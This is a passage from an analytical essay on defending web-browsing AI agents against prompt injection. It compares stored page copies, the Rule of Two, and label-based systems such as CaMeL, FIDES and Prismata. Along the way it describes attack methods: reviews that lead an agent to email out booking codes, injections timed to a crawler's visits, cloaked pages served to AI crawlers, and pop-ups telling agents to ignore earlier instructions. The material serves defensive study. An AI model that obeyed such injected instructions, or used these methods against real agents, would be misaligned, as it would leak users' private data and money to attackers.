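Checking a second page helps only if its author got the information from a different source. Someone who wants to plant a false claim can put it on several sites, and honest writers may copy it. Obscure subjects are easier to exploit. The Eiffel Tower's opening date is on thousands of pages, but a small hotel's bank details may be on only one or two, and an attacker could add a third.

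Outdated pages and the shop pages created by agents' searches can mislead an agent in a similar way, though unintentionally. In all these cases, reading a stored copy is enough to make the agent give a wrong answer. The deposit is lost only if the agent then pays it with a payment tool, or if a user trusts the answer and pays.

### Pages that differ for agents and people

A website can recognise many agents by their headers, network address or behaviour, and send them a different page. Ayush Paul's website did this to Claude. A site might do this for a harmless reason, such as giving agents a shorter version that is easier to process.

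Khodayari and colleagues warn that their survey would miss injections that a site shows only to certain AI agents, because Common Crawl would receive the harmless version. A stored copy would protect the user from such an injection if the site also served the store's crawler the harmless version.

The site could also do the reverse, sending the malicious version only to the crawler that fills an AI company's index and a harmless one to everybody else. All agents using that index would then read the malicious text, while people visiting the site would see nothing wrong. Honest crawlers make themselves easy to recognise. Anthropic, for example, says website operators can easily identify visits from ClaudeBot, the crawler that gathers its training data. Site owners need to recognise crawlers to control their access, but this would also let a hostile site target them.

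### What storage changes

An attacker can't use a stored page to keep trying new injections on the same visitor, because its wording is fixed. The figures for Opus 4.6 show how much repeated attempts can matter. But the attacker can plant several pages, and a model that resists an injection once may follow it the next time, so an injection in a stored page that many agents read still has many chances to succeed.

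The operator of a store can also scan pages before any agent reads them. Khodayari and colleagues collected and processed their 1.2 billion pages in about four weeks, using 50 parallel processes. When someone discovers a new type of injection, the operator can search all the saved pages for it. Software can also scan a live page, but it has to do so while the user waits.

Simple scanning makes many mistakes. Only 43% of the 27,860 phrase matches in Common Crawl were real injections, so blocking every match would remove more harmless passages than malicious ones. Some of the harmless passages are from pages that teach people about prompt injection. The study did not test how much scanning would reduce successful attacks.

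The disadvantage of a store is that it can keep a bad copy of a page after the website has corrected it. When Khodayari and colleagues revisited pages with injections in their HTML elements in January 2026, 34% of those injections were gone. Some had been in job listings that had since closed or forms that had changed. A store that had copied the pages earlier and not refreshed them would still contain the removed injections. The figure is uncertain because some sites may have hidden the text from the researchers' browser, although the researchers rechecked by hand. They did not measure how many agents read the old copies.

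Refreshing stored results frequently wouldn't remove most injections, because many last a long time. Among Internet Archive copies of the same Common Crawl pages, 93% of those from three months earlier already contained an injection, as did 66% of those from a year earlier.

For short-lived injections, a store changes the pattern of exposure more than the average amount. Suppose a malicious review stays on the hotel's page for *d* days, and a crawler visits every *T* days at a time unrelated to the review. If *d* is less than *T*, the chance that the crawler saves the review is *d*/*T*. If it does, the copy stays in the store for *T* days. The average exposure is therefore

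(*d*/*T*) × *T* = *d* days,

the same as on the live page.

If the review is up for one day and the crawler visits every 30 days, the review has a 1 in 30 chance of entering the store, where it would stay for a month. Suppose agents read the page 1,000 times a day and follow the injection 0.6% of the time, the rate for commercial models in the summary test. On the live web, they would follow it about six times. With the store, they would most likely never follow it, but there is a 1 in 30 chance that they would follow it about 180 times over the month.

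An attacker who can predict the crawler's visits can do much better than this average. The owner of a malicious site can see past visits in the server's log, add the injection shortly before the next visit, and remove it afterwards. Text that was live for a few minutes could then stay in the store for a month. The store's operator can make this harder by varying the time of each visit. If somebody notices the bad copy and reports it, the operator can also end the exposure for every user at once by deleting it.

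## How can the origin of content limit an agent's next action?

An agent's risk depends on how its tools combine, so an operator can't judge it by looking at each tool separately. Reading email and searching stored pages do little harm on their own, but if the hotel assistant can also send email, the malicious review may cause it to leak the booking code.

### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

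Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, names three features that together let an attacker steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside world. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this idea into a rule for developers. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injections, an agent should do no more than two of the following in one session:

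- process untrusted input
- access private data or sensitive systems
- change something or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three should be supervised, for example by a person who approves its actions. The last of the three is broader than Willison's, because it includes actions that send no data out, such as deleting a file on the operator's computer.

The table applies both ideas to the hotel assistant, which can read the user's email in every case.

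| Other tools | Untrusted content | Private data | Way to send data out |
|---|---|---|---|
| Live search and page fetch | Yes | Yes | Yes, through web addresses |
| Stored-only search | Yes | Yes | No |
| Stored-only search and email sending | Yes | Yes | Yes, through email |

Adding email sending undoes the protection against leaks, even though the search tool hasn't changed. Taking away the search tool wouldn't fix this, because anyone can put an injection in the user's inbox by sending an email. The operator could instead let the assistant write only to trusted recipients, or have the user check each draft.

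Meta gives the example of a travel assistant that searches the web and has the user's private information. Meta would have the assistant ask before making a reservation or paying a deposit, and would stop it from opening web addresses it constructed itself. The second restriction reduces leaks but doesn't end them, since an agent can still encode private information in its choice of existing addresses.

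The order of tasks can also help. The assistant could research the hotel on the live web before it opens any email, then lose live access for the rest of the session. The malicious review would still be in context when the assistant read the booking code, but the assistant could not send the code out. The user would have to supply the hotel's name and the dates at the start.

Both rules are easy to apply but crude, because they treat an email to the user's partner like an email to a stranger. They also address only prompt injection. Meta warns that an agent that follows the Rule of Two can still make mistakes or give wrong information. The rule would not have prevented the Medicare breach, which involved no prompt injection.

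### Information-flow control

Information-flow control is a more precise method from computer security. Software labels each piece of data by its source, carries the labels through every computation, and checks them before the agent acts. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025) describes how this works for agents.

When a tool returns a value, the value gets the trust label and a second label that lists who may read it. The user and the hotel may read the booking code, and everyone may read a public web page.

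When software or a model combines two values, the result is untrusted if either value was, like the agent's notes described earlier. Its permitted readers are the people who may read both:

readers(*z*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*).

If the user and the hotel may read *x*, and the user and a travel companion may read *y*, only the user may read a text based on both. The software can't determine which parts of the context the model relied on, so it normally gives everything the model writes, including tool calls, the combined label of the whole context.

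Before each tool call, ordinary code applies two rules. An action with consequences must come from a trusted context, and data may go only to its permitted readers. An operator can require both conditions for sending data, or accept either one.

Suppose the assistant has stored-only search and can send email, and the operator trusts emails that the hotel's mail server has authenticated. The malicious review would pass through the system like this:

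1. The user asks about the hotel. The context is trusted.
2. The assistant opens the confirmation email. The context is still trusted, but its permitted readers are now only the user and the hotel.
3. The assistant reads the snapshot with the review. The context becomes untrusted.
4. The injection works, and the model writes a tool call to email the booking code to the reviewer.
5. The code that checks the call finds an untrusted context and a recipient who is not a permitted reader. It blocks the email.

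The check stopped the email even though the model was completely fooled. But it would also block an email the user had asked for, such as a summary of the reviews sent to a travel companion, because that email would also come from an untrusted context and go to someone who is not a permitted reader.

### CaMeL and FIDES

Two systems from 2025, Google DeepMind's CaMeL and Microsoft's FIDES, reduce this problem by keeping untrusted text out of the main model's context. Both use a design that Willison proposed in 2023, in which a planning language model chooses the tool calls without reading untrusted text, and a second, quarantined model reads that text but has no tools. The quarantined model could summarise the hotel's reviews and store the result under a name such as `summary`. The planning model could then email `summary` to the travel companion without seeing what it says. An injection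 in the reviews could corrupt the summary, but it could not make the quarantined model send an email.

In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025), Willison explains a flaw that the DeepMind researchers found in this design. Suppose the user asks the assistant to write to the front desk at the address on the hotel's page. The quarantined model has to find the address, and an injection could make it return the reviewer's address instead. The planning model would then follow its original plan but send the message to the reviewer.

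CaMeL fixes this by labeling each value with its source. Its planning model receives only the user's request and writes the whole plan as a short program in a restricted version of Python. A special interpreter runs the program and keeps track of the labels. Because the front desk's address came from an untrusted page, the interpreter can block the email or ask the user first. CaMeL guarantees that untrusted text can't add a step to the plan, though such text can still affect the plan's values and which of its branches runs.

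FIDES plans one step at a time, so it can adapt to what it finds. It hides a tool's result only if showing it would make the context's label more restrictive. The planning model can read the hidden text if necessary, but it then loses access to some tools. The planning model can also have the quarantined model answer a yes-or-no question. That answer carries only one bit, too little to hold an instruction, so the operator may decide to let the planning model act on it.

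Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES can prevent direct flows of private data to people who shouldn't have it. The proof doesn't cover what an observer could infer from the choice, order and timing of the agent's tool calls. CaMeL's tracking has a similar gap. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) points out that CaMeL doesn't add a private label to a value when private data makes the program skip a line that would have changed it. Suppose a program plans to open page A, but switches to page B if the user's stay is in June. If the stay is in May, the program skips the switch, and the choice of page A carries no private label. The site's owner can still infer that the stay isn't in June.

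Preventing such inferences would require something close to noninterference. Costa and colleagues consider this too restrictive, because it would essentially forbid any call that outsiders can observe once the agent might have read private data. But the restriction would be easier to accept if search used only stored results, because the agent could still look things up.

### What the guarantees cost

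Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo using GPT-4o. The table shows the percentage of ordinary tasks completed without an attack. "Labels only" means an ordinary agent with label checks but no hidden text.

| Tasks | No defence | Labels only | FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Messaging | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

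Against the undefended agent, 152 attacks succeeded, compared with none against either agent with label checks. These counts exclude some cases that AgentDojo scored as successes, including attacks that only changed the wording of a message. Many of the failed banking tasks required the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the checks are designed to prevent. Other tasks failed because GPT-4o mixed up the names of hidden values. With the stronger model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

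*SecureClaw* (2026) reports that none of 629 attacks on CaMeL succeeded, but that CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. The paper's own competing system completed 59. That system's developers ran CaMeL through an adapter, which may have put it at a disadvantage.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) argues that such comparisons are unfair to label-based systems, because the undefended agent acts freely in the test, while a real product would often ask the user to approve its actions. The researchers therefore measured how many tasks an agent could finish without any approval. Using o3-mini, an ordinary agent that needed approval for every consequential action finished 24.3% of tasks this way, and FIDES finished 50.1%.

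Prudentia, which builds on FIDES, finished 59.1% of tasks. It gives the planning model the labels and rules, so the model can avoid steps that would need approval. It can also ask the user to vouch for a piece of text. If an email lists ten jobs for the agent, the user can approve the email once instead of approving ten actions. This saves effort, but a user who overlooks an injection in the email approves that too.

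### Later work on plans, teams and screens

CaMeL checks each step as it runs, so it may discover a forbidden step only after doing most of the work. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, add a check of the whole plan before it starts. One of their rules says that at every point on every possible path through the plan (written **AG**),

**AG**(call_send_money ⇒ ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted)).

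If a plan sends money, neither the recipient nor the amount may come from a tainted source, such as a stranger's web page. If a plan breaks a rule, the checker returns the path that breaks it, and the planning model tries to repair the plan. Rules can also cover the order of events. For example, an operator could require the hotel assistant to confirm the cancellation deadline before it cancels anything.

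Labels can also disappear when one agent hands work to another. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler et al., 2026) tests a team of three agents, each protected by CaMeL, by asking it to send a colleague a summary of job applicants. The first agent read the applicant database, which contained an injection, and the coordinating agent put the summary into its request to the agent that sent messages. That agent treated the whole request as a trusted instruction and also emailed the applicants' details to an outsider.

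Their solution sends instructions and untrusted data through separate channels. On their benchmark, standard attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent, and never with the separate channels. An attacker who knew about the gap left by protecting each agent individually could still target it. Agents completed fewer tasks with the separate channels, though only modestly fewer for the strongest models.

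Agents that operate a screen are harder to protect because they normally look at the screen before each click. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planning model plan for every likely situation in advance. Its plans averaged about 40 branches, compared with four for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo, and roughly half of each plan was for situations that didn't arise. With the most capable models, the system kept up to 57% of normal performance. An attacker could still make the agent follow a harmful branch of the plan. For example, if the plan included closing any cookie notice, an advertisement that looked like one could lead the agent to click it and open a malicious site.

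### Prismata and pages with mixed content

CaMeL's labels work best with tools whose purpose is clear, such as one that sends email. A browser agent mostly clicks, and a click might open a photo or cancel a booking. To find out what a button does, software has to read the page, which may also contain an injection. *Prismata* (Villa, Tan and colleagues, July 2026) tries to solve this by using the page's structure.

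A web page is made up of nested sections. Prismata uses a language model to decide whether the user's task needs each button or link. The model's input is limited to the task, the button or link, and the sections that contain it. A malicious review elsewhere on the page can't influence the decision because it isn't in that input.

A second check works from the outermost section inwards. If it reaches a section headed "Reviews", it labels everything inside as written by users, without reading further. Prismata then removes this text or makes it read-only, depending on the task. Ordinary code rejects any click that the labels don't permit. The hotel assistant could read the reviews but not open the reviewer's link or press a cancel button that its task didn't require.

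Prismata can fail if untrusted text surrounds a button and no heading or other clue comes before it. Villa and colleagues used language models to look for such cases on 5,664 pages and found 94 among 90,408 pieces of untrusted content (0.1%). They reduced the number to 15 by excluding links, reasoning that following a link within a site shouldn't change anything. But the Google Web Accelerator deleted people's pages by following such links, so 0.1% is the safer estimate.

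Prismata was tested on copies of websites with an agent running on GPT-5.4-mini. Each attack was a pop-up advertisement, and it counted as successful if the agent interacted with the ad.

| Pop-up | Attack success without Prismata | With Prismata | Tasks completed without Prismata | With Prismata |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | – | – | 29.9% | 26.6% |
| Offer of a shortcut | 63.9% | 2.1% | 11.2% | 24.4% |
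| False notice that the task is complete | 92.5% | 0.0% | 2.3% | 24.8% |
| Order to ignore earlier instructions | 100.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 19.9% |

When there was no attack, the agent completed about one-ninth fewer tasks with Prismata than without it. In a separate set of 20 tasks, Prismata raised the cost of running the models by 47%, even when it reused earlier labels. This is a good result for a defence that needs no help from website owners. But few tasks require an agent to read advertisements, so Prismata could usually remove them. A malicious review is harder to deal with if the user wants to know what guests think, because Prismata would have to leave the review readable. It could not then stop the agent from misusing a button that the task needs, such as one for messaging the hotel.

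### Detection, training and user confirmation

Operators can also try to detect injections before the agent reads them. *WebSentinel* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) first picks out the parts of a page where attackers tend to put injections, such as pop-ups, forms and comments. A language model then checks whether each part fits the rest of the page. This can catch attacks that contain no instruction, such as a duplicate form that collects personal details. It also identifies the malicious passage, so the site's owner can delete it and find out who posted it. WebSentinel was 12 percentage points more accurate than the best earlier method. A detector like this can work with an existing agent and doesn't restrict the agent's tools on pages that pass.

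Any detector makes mistakes, and an attacker can keep rewriting an injection until the detector misses it. Willison notes that vendors advertise catching 95% of attacks, which in web security is a failing grade. False alarms are also a problem because injections are rare. In the survey by Khodayari and colleagues, about one page in 124,000 contained an injection. A detector that wrongly flagged 1% of clean pages would raise about 1,240 false alarms for each real injection. WebSentinel's test data had nearly three contaminated pages for every clean one, so its accuracy on that data is a poor guide to how many false alarms it would raise on the open web.

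Developers can instead train the model to resist injections. This protects the agent wherever it reads text, including places nobody thought to label. It also lets the agent follow legitimate instructions that strict label checks would block, such as a hotel page's request that late guests email the front desk. The latest models resist injections far better than those of 2025. For tasks that depend on following a stranger's instructions, trained judgement may be the only automatic protection.

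But a model's resistance offers no guarantee, and developers have to test it again for each new model. Kolluri and colleagues cite a study in which attacks defeated a combination of two training methods every time and got past 12 other defences of this general kind with similar ease. Those results concern older methods, but they show how badly a defence can perform once attackers adapt to it.

Asking the user has an advantage over the other defences because the user knows what they wanted. They can catch an agent that has misunderstood the request or invented a fact, even when there is no attack. Label checks would miss these errors if all the data came from trusted sources.

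However, users who see many requests stop reading them, and the testers in Anthropic's study approved most of the dangerous commands. An attacker may also influence the wording of the request. Kolluri and colleagues suggest that the request show the labels and the origin of the data, which the attacker can't change. The hotel assistant's request could show that the recipient's address came from a guest review, which would help the user more than just asking whether to send an email.

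Label checks work well with user confirmation because they can approve most actions and leave only the doubtful ones to the user. In tests by Kolluri and colleagues with o3-mini, an ordinary agent needed about 48 approvals across the tasks it completed, while FIDES needed about 19. People are more likely to read 19 requests than 48, though Kolluri and colleagues assumed that users would approve correctly and did not test real users.

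### Why labels do not stop a false fact

Suppose a user asks the assistant to pay a hotel deposit, and the assistant finds a fake hotel website that lists a scammer's account number. Labels would not protect the user, because the real hotel's account number would also be labeled as coming from an untrusted page.

The operator can forbid payments to account numbers found on untrusted pages, but then the assistant can't make the payment the user asked for. If the operator allows these payments, a scammer who put an account number on the page gets the money. If the assistant asks the user to approve the payment, the user sees an unfamiliar account number and probably can't tell whether it is right.

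Limiting how much information gets through doesn't solve this either. FIDES might reduce a page to a yes-or-no answer about whether cancellation is still free. That answer can't contain an instruction, but if it's wrong, the assistant might cancel too late. Villa and colleagues likewise exclude fake reviews from what Prismata is meant to stop, because an agent choosing the best-reviewed product has to rely on reviews.

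The assistant needs a better source for the fact, such as a contracted booking service or a phone number from an earlier bill. The operator can also limit the damage by capping payments to new recipients, or by delaying the payment long enough for the user to cancel it.
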